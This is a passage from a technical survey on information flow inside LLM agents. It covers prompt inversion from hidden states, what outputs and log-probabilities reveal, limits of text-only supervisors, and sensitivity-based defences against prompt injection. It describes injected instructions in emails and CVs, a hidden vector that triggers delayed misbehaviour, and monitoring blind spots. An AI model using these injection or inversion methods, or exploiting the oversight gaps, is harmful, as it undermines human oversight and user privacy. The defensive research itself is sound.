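A very small model shows how the observable flow can be zero when the internal flow is not. Suppose the supplier's email always confirms delivery but gives the day as either Tuesday or Wednesday, with equal probability. The hidden state has two coordinates:

$$h = (1,\ b), \qquad b = 0 \text{ for Tuesday},\ 1 \text{ for Wednesday}$$

The first coordinate records that the crates arrived, and the second records the untrusted bit. The output is a weighted sum $y = w_1 h_1 + w_2 h_2$, with weights that depend on the user's question. When the user asks whether to pay, the weights are $(1, 0)$, so $y = 1$ for both emails and the planner requests the payment. Then

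$$I(b;y) = 0 \text{ bits}, \qquad I(b;h) = 1 \text{ bit}$$

Later the user asks which day the crates came. This question sets the weights to $(0, 1)$, so $y = b$ and the output carries the whole bit, which was already in the hidden state before the question.

A transformer can behave in the same way. A later question doesn't change the activations at the email's positions, only what attention reads from them. The stored bit could also be more dangerous than a date. An email might contain an instruction to recommend renewal whenever the user mentions the contract, and the planner could process that instruction with no visible effect until the contract came up.

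A proof that covers every possible later question would rule out this delayed effect, because those questions include the one about the day. But as with unwinding, the hidden states could still differ. For example, a third coordinate could also store $b$ and have zero weight for every possible question.

### Different scores, the same token

The choice of a token can hide a difference even when the output does depend on every coordinate. Under greedy decoding, the model always picks the token with the highest score. Suppose only two tokens are possible, and the two emails lead to these scores:

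| Email | Score for "pay" | Score for "wait" | Probability of "pay" | Greedy choice |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Tuesday | 2 | 1 | 0.73 | pay |
| Wednesday | 5 | 1 | 0.98 | pay |

The trace contains "pay" in both cases, although the scores, and therefore the hidden states, differ. Sampling with a fixed seed can also produce the same action from different hidden states. If the model outputs "pay" whenever a random number between 0 and 1 falls below the probability of "pay", a draw of 0.5 gives "pay" for both emails, but a draw of 0.9 gives "wait" for Tuesday's.

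In *Language Models are Injective and Hence Invertible*, Nikolaou, Mencattini and colleagues (2025) took 10,000 Wikipedia passages of 50 tokens, ended each with "Complete this: The quick brown fox jumps over the lazy", and ran them through real models. The next token was "dog" every time, but no two passages gave the same hidden state at the last position. In the final layer of Llama-3.1-8B, the closest two states were a distance of 6.2 apart. The threshold for counting two states as the same was about a millionth.

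### A theorem about distinct prompts

A function is injective if different inputs always give different outputs. Nikolaou and colleagues proved that, under certain conditions, the function from prompts to hidden states is injective with probability one. Let $r(s;\theta)$ be the final-layer activations at the last position for prompt $s$ and weights $\theta$. Then

$$s \ne s' \;\Rightarrow\; r(s;\theta) \ne r(s';\theta) \quad \text{for all prompts } s, s' \text{ up to a fixed length}$$

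The theorem concerns the single list of numbers from which the model computes its next token. Changing the email almost surely changes that list, even if the email is hundreds of tokens back. This is a stronger result than showing that the full hidden state changes, which hardly needs a theorem because the full state, as the term is used here, includes the embeddings, and these already identify the tokens.

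The model must be a transformer in which each position can attend only to itself and earlier positions, with a finite vocabulary and a maximum prompt length. Its components must be real-analytic, which means that near every point they equal a convergent power series. Nikolaou and colleagues checked the activation functions of 18 well-known models, including GPT-2, Llama-3 and DeepSeek-V3, and found that all of them qualify. The initial weights must come from a continuous random distribution, training must consist of a finite number of gradient-descent steps with step sizes between 0 and 1, and all arithmetic must be exact.

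The proof begins with two different prompts and considers the squared distance between their states as a function of the weights:

$$g(\theta) = \lVert r(s;\theta) - r(s';\theta) \rVert^2$$

A real-analytic function is either zero everywhere or zero only on a set with no volume. One choice of weights that gives the two prompts different final states rules out the first case. If the prompts differ in their last token, switching off the rest of the network leaves just that token's embedding and position as the final state. If they differ earlier, an attention head can copy information from the first position where they differ. The set of weights that give both prompts the same final state therefore has no volume. There are finitely many pairs of prompts, so the set of weights that do this for at least one pair also has no volume, and a random initialisation avoids it with probability one.

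Training could in principle move the weights onto this set. Nikolaou and colleagues show that a gradient step can stretch or bend a region of possible weights but, apart from a set of exceptions with no volume, cannot flatten it to zero volume. The probability of a collision is therefore still zero after any finite number of steps.

Suppose a model with one weight $\theta$ turns one email into the number $\theta$ and another into $\theta^2$. These are equal only at $\theta = 0$ and $\theta = 1$, and a weight drawn at random from a continuous range will almost surely be neither. But at $\theta = 0.999999$, they differ by only about a millionth. The theorem rules out exact collisions but doesn't set a minimum distance between the states.

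Someone can also build a collision deliberately by giving two tokens exactly the same embedding, so that swapping one for the other changes nothing inside the model. *Transformer Injectivity & Geometric Robustness* (von Strauss, 2025) extends the result to every layer and to a broader class of training methods, but its proof does not cover gradient clipping or low-precision weight updates, both of which developers commonly use. The theorem therefore gives strong reason to expect distinct states in a commercial model, but does not guarantee them.

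The same argument applies to the model's next-token probabilities. Hu, Koyejo and Potts (2026) sketch this extension in *Verbalizing Subliminal Learning Effects Using Text Optimization*. It requires only weights that keep the two prompts distinct after the softmax. So in the idealised model, the difference between two emails also reaches the probabilities, and disappears from the trace only when the model picks one token.

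In case A, if two emails lead to different token probabilities, the planner's sampled output must differ for some random draws. The chance of a visible difference may be tiny, but noninterference requires the payment to be strictly independent of the email. A step after the probabilities are computed, such as greedy decoding or a runtime that refuses the payment, therefore has to discard the difference.

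### Searching for collisions

Nikolaou and colleagues compared 100,000 prompts from Wikipedia, web pages, computer code and other text, looking for two different prompts that gave a model the same hidden state. They made about five billion comparisons per model and found no such pair in any layer of any model they tested. In Llama-3.1-8B, the smallest distance between two prompts' hidden states was 0.001 after the first layer and 0.62 after the last.

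They then took the ten prompts with the closest states and added every token in the vocabulary to each, which gave more than 343 billion pairs per model for GPT-2 Small and Gemma3-1B. They again found no collisions. The closest pairs they examined in two larger models were nearly identical pieces of Python code, most of which differed only in the number of trailing newlines.

These tests are reassuring about ordinary text, but 100,000 prompts are a tiny fraction of all possible prompts, and an attacker could search for unusual ones. An attacker would rarely gain from a collision, though, because an injection that produced exactly the same state as a harmless email would also have the same effect on the next token.

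### Recovering the email from the activations

If each prompt produces a different hidden state, someone who has the state should be able to work out the prompt. Nikolaou and colleagues do this with an algorithm called SIPIT, which needs the model's weights and the activations at every position in one layer. It tries candidates for the first token until one reproduces the first position's activations, then keeps that token and does the same for each later position. A 20-token prompt from a vocabulary of 50,000 takes at most a million trials, compared with $50{,}000^{20}$ for testing every complete prompt.

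SIPIT recovered all 100 test prompts of 20 tokens exactly from GPT-2 Small, in an average of 28 seconds each. Using gradients to choose which tokens to try first made it more than 100 times faster than trying them in random order. It also recovered all 50 ten-token prompts in a test on versions of Mistral-7B and Llama-3.1-8B with weights compressed to four bits. In principle, the hidden state at the last position alone is enough to identify the prompt, but Nikolaou and colleagues leave an efficient method for that to future work.

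Słowikowski and Majewski (2026), in *Recovering Input Text from Hidden States*, studied a different search on GPT-2 Small. For each position, they adjusted an artificial embedding by gradient descent until it produced nearly the right final-layer activations, then looked for a real token among its nearest neighbours. They recovered 66.9% of ten-token prompts exactly with up to 1,000 steps and 2,000 candidate tokens per position, and 97.5% with 2,000 steps and 10,000 candidates.

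In a comparison on 100 prompts, SIPIT recovered all of them at 0.65 seconds per token, while the more thorough version of the paper's own search recovered 96% at 30.6 seconds per token. The words the slower method missed were therefore present in the activations, so most of its errors came from the search.

Common words and punctuation, such as "the", "of" and the comma, caused most of the failures because their embeddings are close together. Names, digits and technical terms were much easier to recover, so the account number in a supplier's email would probably be easier than the words around it. Someone running the search can tell when it has failed without knowing the original text, because a wrong token leaves a large mismatch with the observed activations.

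Both studies used short prompts. *Depth Gives a False Sense of Privacy* (2025) reports recovering sensitive prompts of up to 4,112 tokens from internal states, including those of deep layers, although not all of its attacks are designed to recover the exact text.

### How large is the difference, and does it matter?

Zero dependence is therefore false for almost any weights once the email is in the planner's context, because changing the email changes the hidden state. If the hidden state identifies the email, the mutual information $I(X;H)$ equals the email's entropy, which is its maximum. The planner in case A can request the same payment for every email while its hidden state holds all the information in each one.

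But the difference between two states may be very small. *Transformers need glasses! Information over-squashing in language tasks* (2024) proves that, under certain conditions, if two prompts differ only by one extra copy of the last token, their final states grow arbitrarily close as the prompts get longer. Eventually the gap is too small for the computer's arithmetic to represent. *TIDE* (2026) found that the states of certain pairs of tokens in a one-billion-parameter Llama model stayed close together until the last few layers.

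Von Strauss measured how far the state moves per changed token and found that, for the least sensitive pairs of prompts, this distance tends to shrink as prompts get longer. This is weaker evidence than it seems, because two unrelated 500-token prompts differ in far more places than two 16-token prompts. The distance per changed token would therefore fall even if the distance between their states stayed the same.

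Rounding limits the theorem more directly. In a model of width 768 with 16-bit numbers, the last position's state can hold at most 12,288 bits, but a 1,000-token prompt can carry about 15,600. So some different prompts must produce the same last-position state, even though no such pair appeared in the tests.

Von Strauss gives a condition under which rounding is harmless. If the closest two states in a set of prompts are a distance $m$ apart, any error smaller than $m/2$ in each state leaves them distinct. Rounding each of $d$ coordinates to the nearest multiple of $\delta$ moves a state by at most $\sqrt{d}\,\delta/2$, so it is enough that

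$$\delta < \frac{m}{\sqrt{d}}$$

With 4,096 coordinates and a smallest distance of 0.64 between activations, rounding in steps finer than 0.01 cannot make any two collide. When von Strauss rounded the saved activations of Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct to eight bits, no sampled prompts collided, but at four bits 1,713 pairs did. Nikolaou and colleagues found no collisions in models with four-bit weights, but they did not round the activations so coarsely.

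A difference in the hidden state also doesn't need to mean anything. The theorem already holds at initialisation, when the weights are random and the model has learned nothing. Such a model can't recognise a delivery date or an instruction, but its last-position state almost surely differs for every email. Adding a newline to the end of the supplier's email would almost surely change the state, and so would adding an order to redirect the payment.

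## How much of the hidden state can be inferred from outputs?

Someone who watches the runtime has a model's outputs and wants to infer its activations. The opposite problem, recovering the text that produced a given set of activations, can often be solved. Control engineers also have to infer a machine's internal state from its outputs when sensors can't measure that state directly. They call a system observable if its outputs determine its internal state.

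### States that no question can separate

Two internal states can give the same output now and different outputs later. They are Nerode equivalent if they give the same outputs for every future sequence of inputs. If a system is secure, this relation can always be used in an unwinding proof of its security. For a model that samples its tokens, equivalent states must give the same output probabilities. Someone who knew how the planner would respond to every possible continuation would therefore know its state up to equivalence. That includes everything about the state that can affect behaviour, but not the rest, such as a coordinate that always has zero weight.

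A trace contains only one continuation, so it reveals much less. Ten yes-or-no outputs can separate at most 1,024 states. The observer can't try the other continuations by carrying on the conversation, because each new question changes the context. They would have to return to the same saved state for each one, and a vocabulary of 50,000 tokens allows about $10^{47}$ follow-ups of just ten tokens.

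Equivalence also depends on what the observer sees. A noninterference proof for payments shows that the planner's states after all possible emails are equivalent for an observer who sees only payments. An observer who also reads the planner's messages could tell many of those states apart.

### A language model as a sliding window

Liu, Soatto and colleagues (2024), in *Meanings and Feelings of Large Language Models*, applied observability to language models. They describe a model as a window of $c$ tokens that moves forward by one token at each step:

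$$x_i(t+1) = x_{i+1}(t) \ \text{ for } i < c, \qquad x_c(t+1) = \pi\big(\phi(x_1(t), \ldots, x_c(t))\big)$$

The function $\phi$ turns the window into activations, and $\pi$ picks the next token based on them. Liu and colleagues call the window the model's state and the activations its "mental state", so their "mental state" corresponds to the hidden state.

Their first theorem assumes that $\phi$ and $\pi$ are deterministic. An observer who records the outputs then knows the last $t$ tokens of the window after $t$ steps, and the whole window after $c$ steps, because every output token enters the window and pushes out the oldest one. If a three-token window starts as "check the email" and the model outputs "delivery", "confirmed" and "today", the window then consists of those three words. An observer who can also see the starting text knows the whole window from the beginning.

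The theorem recovers text, but computing the activations from that text requires the model's weights. In case A, an operator running an open-weights planner on a stateless server has the weights, and the runtime has the whole context, so the operator could rerun the model and record the activations at every layer and position. This gives the exact hidden state for an email that has arrived, but it doesn't bound the hidden state that a different email would produce.

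### When part of the prompt is hidden

Liu and colleagues also consider models that feed vectors, instead of tokens, back into their own input. They prove that such a model can be built to give the same output for every starting text, so an observer learns nothing about the text from the output. They do not prove this for every model of this kind.

They then return to models that output tokens and add one slot at the front of the window that the user can't see. They test four ways of filling it:

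- **Type 1** holds a fixed token, like a one-word system prompt.
- **Type 2** holds a fixed vector that need not match any token.
- **Type 3** holds a mixture of the $m$ highest-scoring tokens from the previous step.
- **Type 4** holds a running average of such mixtures over all earlier steps.

Liu and colleagues tested GPT-2 (2019) and LLaMA-2-7B (2023) with greedy decoding. They took visible prompts from a collection of film-review sentences, generated up to 100 tokens with each hidden setting, and counted how many settings led to exactly the same text. The table gives the largest share of hidden trajectories that an observer could not tell apart.

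| Type | What the observer does not know | GPT-2 | LLaMA-2-7B |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Which of 100 tokens is in the slot | 35% | 20% |
| 2 | Which vector is in the slot | 70% | 15% |
| 3 | The value of $m$, from 1 to 20 | 80% | 30% |
| 4 | The value of $m$, from 1 to 20 | more than one trajectory | more than one trajectory |

None of the four types was observable, although Liu and colleagues also conclude that standard language models are. The two findings are compatible because the positive theorem assumes that the recorded window contains everything the model uses, and in each of the four types, some of that is outside the window. In these experiments, the hidden setting was the part of the input that the observer lacked. Each setting corresponded to one trajectory of activations, so an observer who learned the setting could recompute the activations.

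A well-chosen prompt can reveal more. Liu and colleagues optimised a visible prompt to make GPT-2 respond differently to 1,000 possible hidden tokens. This reduced the largest group of tokens that could not be told apart to about 1% of the total, or around ten. The percentages come from small, old models with one-slot prompts, so they are a poor guide to current systems. But in any model, a hidden input can prevent an observer from inferring the hidden state from a finite trace.

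Liu and colleagues also showed that a difference between hidden states can appear late in the output. Their search took less than ten minutes on consumer graphics cards and found a hidden vector that made LLaMA-2-7B behave normally at first and then misbehave. When asked whether large language models are dangerous, the model began with the same sentence as it did with a harmless hidden prompt, then told the user to visit a website. The two internal states are not Nerode equivalent, but a trace that ended after the first sentence would not have distinguished them.

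The positive theorem applies to an operator who records the planner's full context. It does not apply to a company that rents a model if the provider adds instructions or memory of its own, or to anyone in case C who sees the quarantined model's one-word answer but not the email.

### From log-probabilities to the last layer

An output token reveals only which token was chosen based on the model's scores. Some services also return log-probabilities, the logarithms of the probabilities that the model gave to particular tokens. Nazir, Finlayson and colleagues (2025) show in *Better Language Model Inversion by Compactly Representing Next-Token Distributions* that log-probabilities reveal much more than the output tokens alone.

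Let $h$ be the $D$ numbers from which the model computes its scores, and let $w_k$ be the row of the output matrix for token $k$. The score for that token is $w_k \cdot h$, so its log-probability is

$$\log p_k = w_k \cdot h - \log \sum_j e^{w_j \cdot h}$$

The last term is the same for every token. It is there because adding the same amount to every score does not change the probabilities. Subtracting the log-probability of one reference token $r$ removes it:

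$$\log p_k - \log p_r = (w_k - w_r) \cdot h$$

Each token after the first gives one linear equation in the $D$ unknown entries of $h$. With $D+1$ log-probabilities we have $D$ equations, which determine $h$ exactly if they are independent.

Suppose $h$ has two coordinates and there are three tokens, "pay", "wait" and "stop", with rows $(1,0)$, $(0,1)$ and $(0,0)$. An observer who sees probabilities of 0.665, 0.245 and 0.090 can compute $\ln(0.665/0.090) \approx 2$ and $\ln(0.245/0.090) \approx 1$, so $h \approx (2, 1)$. An observer who saw only the greedy choice, "pay", would learn only that the first coordinate was larger than the second and not negative.

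The method requires a known output matrix of full column rank, so every direction in $h$ affects at least one score. It also requires that no direction raise every score equally, because the softmax would cancel its effect. An observer who does not know the matrix can still recover $h$ up to an unknown linear transformation. Nazir and colleagues found that some sets of tokens gave nearly dependent equations, so they used 100 more tokens than the minimum.

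The recovered state also differs slightly from the last layer's raw output. *The Smallest Singular Directions of the Unembedding Matter Disproportionately for Next-Token Prediction* (2026) explains that models first divide that output by its scale, so its overall size is lost. The output matrix also amplifies some directions much more than others. If it multiplies a direction by $\sigma$, an error of $\varepsilon$ along that direction in the equations becomes an error of $\varepsilon/\sigma$ in the recovered state. Rounded log-probabilities may therefore reveal little about the directions the matrix amplifies least.

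This algebra gives an upper limit on displacement, which a proof about payments cannot do. Let $A$ be the matrix with rows $w_k - w_r$ for the chosen tokens, and let $\sigma_{\min}$ be the smallest factor by which it stretches any direction. If changing the email changes each of the $D$ differences in log-probability by at most $\varepsilon$, then

$$\lVert h - h' \rVert \;\le\; \frac{\sqrt{D}\,\varepsilon}{\sigma_{\min}}$$

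With $D = 768$, $\varepsilon = 0.01$ and $\sigma_{\min} = 0.1$, the state moves by at most about 2.8. If the log-probabilities never changed, neither would the state. It is hard to prove for every email that the log-probabilities change this little or not at all. The agent proofs described earlier establish this only when the email stays out of the planner's context, and then the whole hidden state is the same anyway.

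Even an exact $h$ describes only the last layer at one position. The equations don't determine earlier layers, because different activations can lead to the same result. If an early layer computes two numbers and a later layer keeps only their sum, then 1 and 4 give the same result as 2 and 3. However, if different prompts always produce different states, someone with the weights could in principle identify the prompt from $h$ and recompute every layer, within the limits of search time and rounding. Słowikowski and Majewski report that GPT-2 meets the conditions for different prompts to produce different states.

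### Two models that behave alike

Suppose a company replaces its planner with a new model that gives almost the same answers. In *When Does Closeness in Distribution Imply Representational Similarity?*, Nielsen, Marconato and colleagues (2025) examine when findings about the old model's hidden states also apply to the new one.

They start from a known theorem about models that end in a softmax. If two models give every token the same probability after every input, their last-layer representations $f$ and $f'$ are related by an invertible matrix $B$:

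$$f(x) = B\,f'(x) \quad \text{for every input } x$$

The theorem assumes that the models' representations and output vectors vary in every available direction. The matrix can rotate or stretch the space, but it preserves the information and any property that a linear probe can read.

Real models' outputs agree only approximately, and Nielsen and colleagues prove that such agreement may not guarantee any linear similarity between their hidden states. They measure agreement by the Kullback-Leibler (KL) divergence, a standard measure in training that is zero when two sets of probabilities are identical. In their construction, both models give almost all the probability to the same token for each input. Each model's hidden states cluster by token, but the clusters are arranged differently in the two models. No linear map can undo this rearrangement, which affects only the tiny probabilities of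 the other tokens. As Nielsen and colleagues lengthened the output vectors from 3 to 18, the divergence fell from 0.89 to 0.0001, while a measure of linear similarity, which is 1 for a perfect match, never exceeded 0.001.

A milder version appeared in image classifiers trained twice in the same way. The two runs had almost the same test loss, but images of trucks lay between cars and ships in one and between cars and horses in the other, and the similarity between the two runs was 0.55. These classifiers had to fit ten classes into two dimensions, and their KL divergence of about 1.1 was not small, so the example is weak evidence about large language models.

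Nielsen and colleagues define a different measure of agreement that does give a guarantee. This distance compares how log-probabilities vary across inputs and tokens. If two models with $M$-dimensional representations are within $\varepsilon$ of each other by this distance, a measure of dissimilarity between their representations is at most $2M\varepsilon$. The dissimilarity cannot exceed 1 anyway, so for $M = 768$ the bound is informative only if $\varepsilon$ is below about 0.00065.

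Nielsen, Marconato and colleagues (2026), in *Logit Distance Bounds Representational Similarity*, obtain a similar guarantee from the distance between the models' scores. They also show what it would take to use the KL divergence instead. If no token ever has a probability below $\tau$, then

$$d_{\text{score}}^2 \;\le\; \frac{4(\log \tau)^2}{\tau}\, d_{\text{KL}}$$

With 50,000 tokens, $\tau$ is at most 1 in 50,000, so the divergence is multiplied by at least 23 million. Both papers cover only the last representations before the softmax, and the 2025 paper calls the same question for earlier layers an open problem. So a test that finds two planners' answers almost indistinguishable does not show that their hidden states represent an email in the same way.

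### A supervisor who sees only text

*Epistemic Observability in Language Models* (Mason and Anand, 2026) argues that a supervisor who sees only a model's text can't reliably distinguish honest answers from plausible inventions. It proves two theorems under different assumptions.

The first theorem concerns a model whose answer depends only on the question. Their example asks what a certain Dr Yamamoto's 2021 study concluded. If the study exists, an honest model should report its conclusion, and if it doesn't, the model should decline to answer. Suppose honesty requires the right response with probability at least $1 - \varepsilon$ in each case. The model receives the same question in both, so its two probabilities would have to satisfy

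$$2(1-\varepsilon) \le 1$$

which is false whenever $\varepsilon$ is below one half.

The result is correct, but its proof does not depend on the supervisor's limited view. The model's activations would also be the same in both cases, so a supervisor who could read all of them would do no better. The result does not apply to a planner that has read an email or retrieved a document that differs between the two cases.

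The second theorem allows the model to retrieve documents, but it assumes that checking a particular answer takes more resources than the supervisor has. The supervisor then sees the same thing whether the answer is true or invented, and gives the same reward. Mason and Anand conclude that training can't make the model behave differently in the two cases. This follows if each training update depends only on what the supervisor saw. In ordinary reinforcement learning, the update also depends on the documents the model retrieved, and the model might generalise from questions the supervisor could check.

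Their experiments suggest that text carries some information about honesty. They report results as an AUC, the chance that a score ranks a randomly chosen correct answer above a randomly chosen invention, so 0.5 is no better than guessing. Response length alone had an AUC of 0.63. The models' stated confidence had an AUC of 0.28 to 0.36, so they tended to be more confident when inventing. A supervisor who knew this could reverse the ranking and get 0.64 to 0.72.

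The spread of the model's token probabilities did somewhat better, at 0.757. Mason and Anand exclude services that return log-probabilities from their impossibility result. The theorems therefore support only the conclusion that a supervisor who sees nothing but the text cannot distinguish two cases that produce identical text. A model's written reasoning is also text, and Wang (2026) argues in *LLM Reasoning Is Latent, Not the Chain of Thought* that it gives only a partial view of the reasoning in the hidden states.

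### What competent behaviour requires

Behaviour can also show that a model must contain certain information. *General agents contain world models* (Richens, Abel and colleagues, 2025) proves that an agent competent at enough goals must encode how its environment works.

The environment has a finite number of states, and each action leads from one state to another with a fixed probability. The agent can see the current state, and can get from any state to any other. Its goals are sequences of up to $n$ steps, such as reaching one state and then another. For every such goal, its chance of success is at least $1-\delta$ times the best possible chance. If $P$ is the true probability that an action leads to a given state, one can work out an estimate $\hat{P}$ from the agent's choices alone, with

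$$|\hat{P} - P| \;\le\; \sqrt{\frac{2P(1-P)}{(n-1)(1-\delta)}}$$

The method offers the agent pairs of goals and records which it pursues. Suppose a supplier answers each reminder with some fixed probability. The agent can press one button and aim for at most 20 answers to 100 reminders, or press another and aim for more than 20. A competent agent presses the button for the more likely outcome. Repeating the offer with other thresholds shows where its choice switches, and dividing that threshold by 100 gives an estimate of the probability. For $P = 0.2$, $\delta = 0.1$ and $n = 101$, the theorem limits the error to about 0.06.

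Richens and colleagues tested a version of the method in a random environment with 20 states and five actions. It recovered the probabilities with a low average error, even though the agent failed completely at some goals. They also prove that the result requires goals with more than one step, because an agent can be optimal for immediate goals without its choices revealing anything about the probabilities.

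*General Agents Contain World Models, even under Partial Observability and Stochasticity* (Cifuentes, 2026) extends the theorem to agents that choose at random, provided $\delta$ is below one half, and to agents that cannot see the full state. The second extension depends on defining goals in terms of the environment's true states, so an agent may achieve a goal without knowing it. If the goals referred only to what the agent can see, and every state looked the same, an optimal agent would not need to know the probabilities.

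In these theorems, "encode" means that someone could calculate the probabilities from the agent's policy, the rule that gives its action for every goal and history. Richens and colleagues do not locate the information in any activation or claim that the agent uses it to plan. For a language model, much of it could be in the weights, which stay the same from one call to the next. During a single choice between two buttons, the hidden state only has to contain enough information to make that choice, which is at most one bit.

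The result is still only a lower bound, for the same reason as in the data-processing inequality. The weights and activations must contain whatever can be inferred about the environment from the agent's choices, but they may contain much more. Richens and colleagues note that an agent could know its environment well and still plan badly, in which case their method would underestimate its knowledge.

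## How far can sensitivity analysis bound the influence of a piece of text?

An operator who runs an open-weights planner can examine its hidden state directly instead of inferring it from outputs. After the supplier's email arrives, the operator can calculate how much a slight change to any passage would change the activations and the next token. Researchers developed this kind of sensitivity analysis mainly to solve a practical problem with labels.

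### Narrowing the labels

When an untrusted email enters the planner's context, the conservative rule labels everything the planner produces afterwards as untrusted. To find out how often this is too strict, Xu and colleagues studied programs that insert values, such as a user's question or a retrieved document, into prompts. The programs came from 2,103 families of open-source repositories. Between 12% and 14% of the inserted values had no visible effect on the model's output. The rule is therefore right about most inputs, but it also labels some output as untrusted because of text that had no visible effect on it.

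Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues (2024), in *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, proposed keeping only the labels of documents that influenced the reply. Their method first runs the model on the full context $C$ to get a reply $y$. It then takes only the documents with a more permissive label $L'$, for example the trusted ones, and checks how well the model predicts the same reply from those. The measure is perplexity (PPL), roughly the number of equally likely tokens the model is choosing among at each step. The method may drop the other documents if

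$$\mathrm{PPL}(y \mid C_{L'}) - \mathrm{PPL}(y \mid C) \le \lambda$$

where $\lambda$ is a tolerance. If the planner's reply has a perplexity of 1.20 with the supplier's email and 1.25 without it, a tolerance of 0.1 allows the method to drop the email. Testing labels instead of individual documents saves work. Ten documents have 1,024 subsets, but with only two labels there is a single reduced context to test.

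The method then runs the model again on the reduced context and returns the new reply with the more permissive label. This second run matters more for the hidden state than the measurement does, because the email is no longer in the context and the exclusion argument applies. However, the email's wording helped determine whether the method dropped it, and with two labels that decision can reveal one bit about the email. In tests on agent conversations, the method gave a more permissive label than the baseline in over 85% of cases.

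*RTBAS* (Zhong, Chen and colleagues, 2025) points out that this search still needs many model calls when there are more labels, and estimates 16 to 64 extra calls for typical systems with four to six levels. It instead uses a screener to select the passages that the agent's next step depends on. The screener is either another language model or a small classifier that uses attention scores. For each passage, the classifier takes the attention weights that connect the passage to the output and multiplies each weight by the effect that changing that weight would have on the model's prediction.

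Zhong and colleagues calculated these scores with OPT-125m, an open model with 125 million parameters, even though GPT-4o and Claude had produced the agents' actions. After training on labelled AgentDojo cases, the classifier was right 81% of the time on test data. The runtime joins the labels of the passages that the classifier selects, then redacts every message with a more restrictive label before it calls the planner. If the classifier wrongly judges the supplier's email irrelevant, the runtime removes both the email and its label from the context. The error rate would be worrying if the runtime removed only the label. Because it removes the text too, mistakes can deprive the agent of information it needs or cause unnecessary requests for the user's confirmation, but they do not let text influence the planner without its label being counted. Zhong and colleagues report that RTBAS stopped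 every AgentDojo attack that violated its policies and reduced task completion by less than 2%.

According to Xu and colleagues, *Ghost in the Agent* (2026) tracks the meaning of untrusted text through recordings of an agent's steps. Štorek and colleagues' Geometric Information Flow (GIF) and Xu and colleagues' Sightline work inside a single model call. Both leave the text in the context and estimate its influence on the output. An operator can use such an estimate to remove a label, but this doesn't change the planner's hidden state, because the planner has already read the email by then.

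### From a small change to a number of bits

GIF starts with one recorded prompt, one passage in it, and one position where the model is about to produce a token. Let $x$ be the list of embeddings for the passage. GIF adds a small random change $u$ to $x$ and keeps the rest of the prompt constant. Each number in $u$ comes from a normal distribution with mean zero and variance $\tau$.

The change first reaches the hidden state $h$ from which the model computes its scores. If $J$ is the Jacobian of $h$ with respect to the passage's embeddings, then for small $u$

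$$h(x+u) \approx h(x) + Ju$$

The output matrix $W$ turns this into a change of $WJu$ in the scores. How much the probabilities then change depends on what they were to begin with. With only two tokens, raising the score of one by $\delta$ has an effect proportional to $p(1-p)\,\delta^2$, where $p$ is that token's probability. The factor $p(1-p)$ is 0.25 when the model is undecided and about 0.01 when it is 99% sure. For a whole vocabulary, the corresponding weights form the Fisher information matrix

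$$F = \mathrm{diag}(p) - pp^{\top}$$

Putting the steps together gives the KL divergence between the new token probabilities and the old ones, to a good approximation:

$$\mathrm{KL} \approx \tfrac{1}{2}\, u^{\top} M u, \qquad M = J^{\top} W^{\top} F\, W J$$

To get a number of bits, Štorek and colleagues replace the model with a simpler channel that has the same local sensitivity. Its input is the random change $U$ and its output is $AU + N$, where $A = F^{1/2}WJ$ and $N$ is random noise with variance 1 in each coordinate. This is a Gaussian channel, and information theory has an exact formula for how much its output reveals about its input. The GIF score is

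$$\mathrm{GIF} = \tfrac{1}{2}\log_2 \det\left(I + \tau A A^{\top}\right)$$

The singular values of $A$ are the factors by which it stretches changes in different directions. If they are $s_1, s_2, \ldots$, the score is the sum of $\tfrac{1}{2}\log_2(1+\tau s_i^2)$. Suppose there are two, 3 and 0.1, and $\tau = 1$. Then

$$\tfrac{1}{2}\log_2(1+9) + \tfrac{1}{2}\log_2(1+0.01) \approx 1.661 + 0.007 \approx 1.67 \text{ bits}$$

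Almost all of the flow comes from the first direction. A change along the second is too weak for an observer to distinguish from the noise.

### What the Lean proof covers

Štorek and colleagues prove that the score does not underestimate the true flow when the changes are small enough. Let $Y$ now be the token that the real model samples. Then

$$I(U;Y) \;\le\; \mathrm{GIF} + o(\tau)$$

where $o(\tau)$ is an error that shrinks faster than $\tau$ as $\tau$ approaches zero.

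The true flow is the average KL divergence between the token probabilities after each change and their mean over all changes. This mean is hard to compute, so the proof replaces it with the token probabilities for the original prompt, which can only make the result larger. For small changes, this upper bound and the GIF score are both close to $\tfrac{\tau}{2}$ times the sum of the squared singular values (divided by $\ln 2$ to get bits).

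In the example, the approximation is close at $\tau = 0.01$, where the formula with squared singular values gives 0.065 bits and the GIF score is 0.062 bits. It fails at $\tau = 1$, where they are 6.5 and 1.67 bits. The theorem does not give a value of $\tau$ below which the error is negligible.

Štorek and colleagues checked the mathematics in Lean. They assume that near the recorded prompt, the hidden state differs from the linear approximation by at most a constant times the squared size of the change. They do not verify this assumption for any deployed model, and they state that the proof certifies only the mathematical claim. The claim covers small changes to one passage in one prompt and their effect on the next token.

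The score also measures influence on the token, not on the hidden state. If a change moves $h$ far in a direction to which $W$ or $F$ gives almost no weight, the score will still be close to zero. Applying the same calculation to the hidden state would not help, because the hidden state has no random noise. In exact arithmetic, if the hidden state depended even slightly on the continuous change $U$, it would reveal $U$ to unlimited precision in some direction, and the mutual information would be infinite.

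### Finding the passages that matter

Computing the whole Jacobian of a large model would take thousands of backward passes, so GIF estimates the sum of the Jacobian's squared singular values by sending a few random changes through the model and back. In a test on 150 tokens from AgentDojo tool calls, the estimates ranked the passages accurately but were poor measures of how large each passage's influence was. With the largest number of random changes tested, their rank correlation with the exact scores was 0.988, but their average relative error was still 36%.

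In the hiring example, the agent recommends an unqualified applicant because hidden text in the CV tells it to. The hidden text gets 82 bits, compared with 27 for the trusted instructions and 16 for everything else, so the ranking correctly identifies the source of the recommendation. The values themselves are harder to interpret, because they depend on the choice of $\tau$ and because the theorem covers one token while the recommendation contains many.

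Štorek and colleagues tested the rankings on three benchmarks with six open-weights models. For each agent run, they took the 50 tokens with the highest GIF scores and calculated the share that belonged to a planted injection or a private fact. A useful score should give a higher share when the agent broke the policy. The table shows the AUC averaged over the six models, where guessing would give 0.5. "Gradient only" is a simpler score based on the chosen token alone, and "RTBAS attention" is the RTBAS screener without the redaction that makes it safe.

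| Benchmark | GIF | Gradient only | RTBAS attention |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo (prompt injection) | 0.91 | 0.90 | 0.84 |
| MSB (prompt injection) | 0.92 | 0.92 | 0.76 |
| AgentDAM (private data) | 0.75 | 0.74 | 0.57 |

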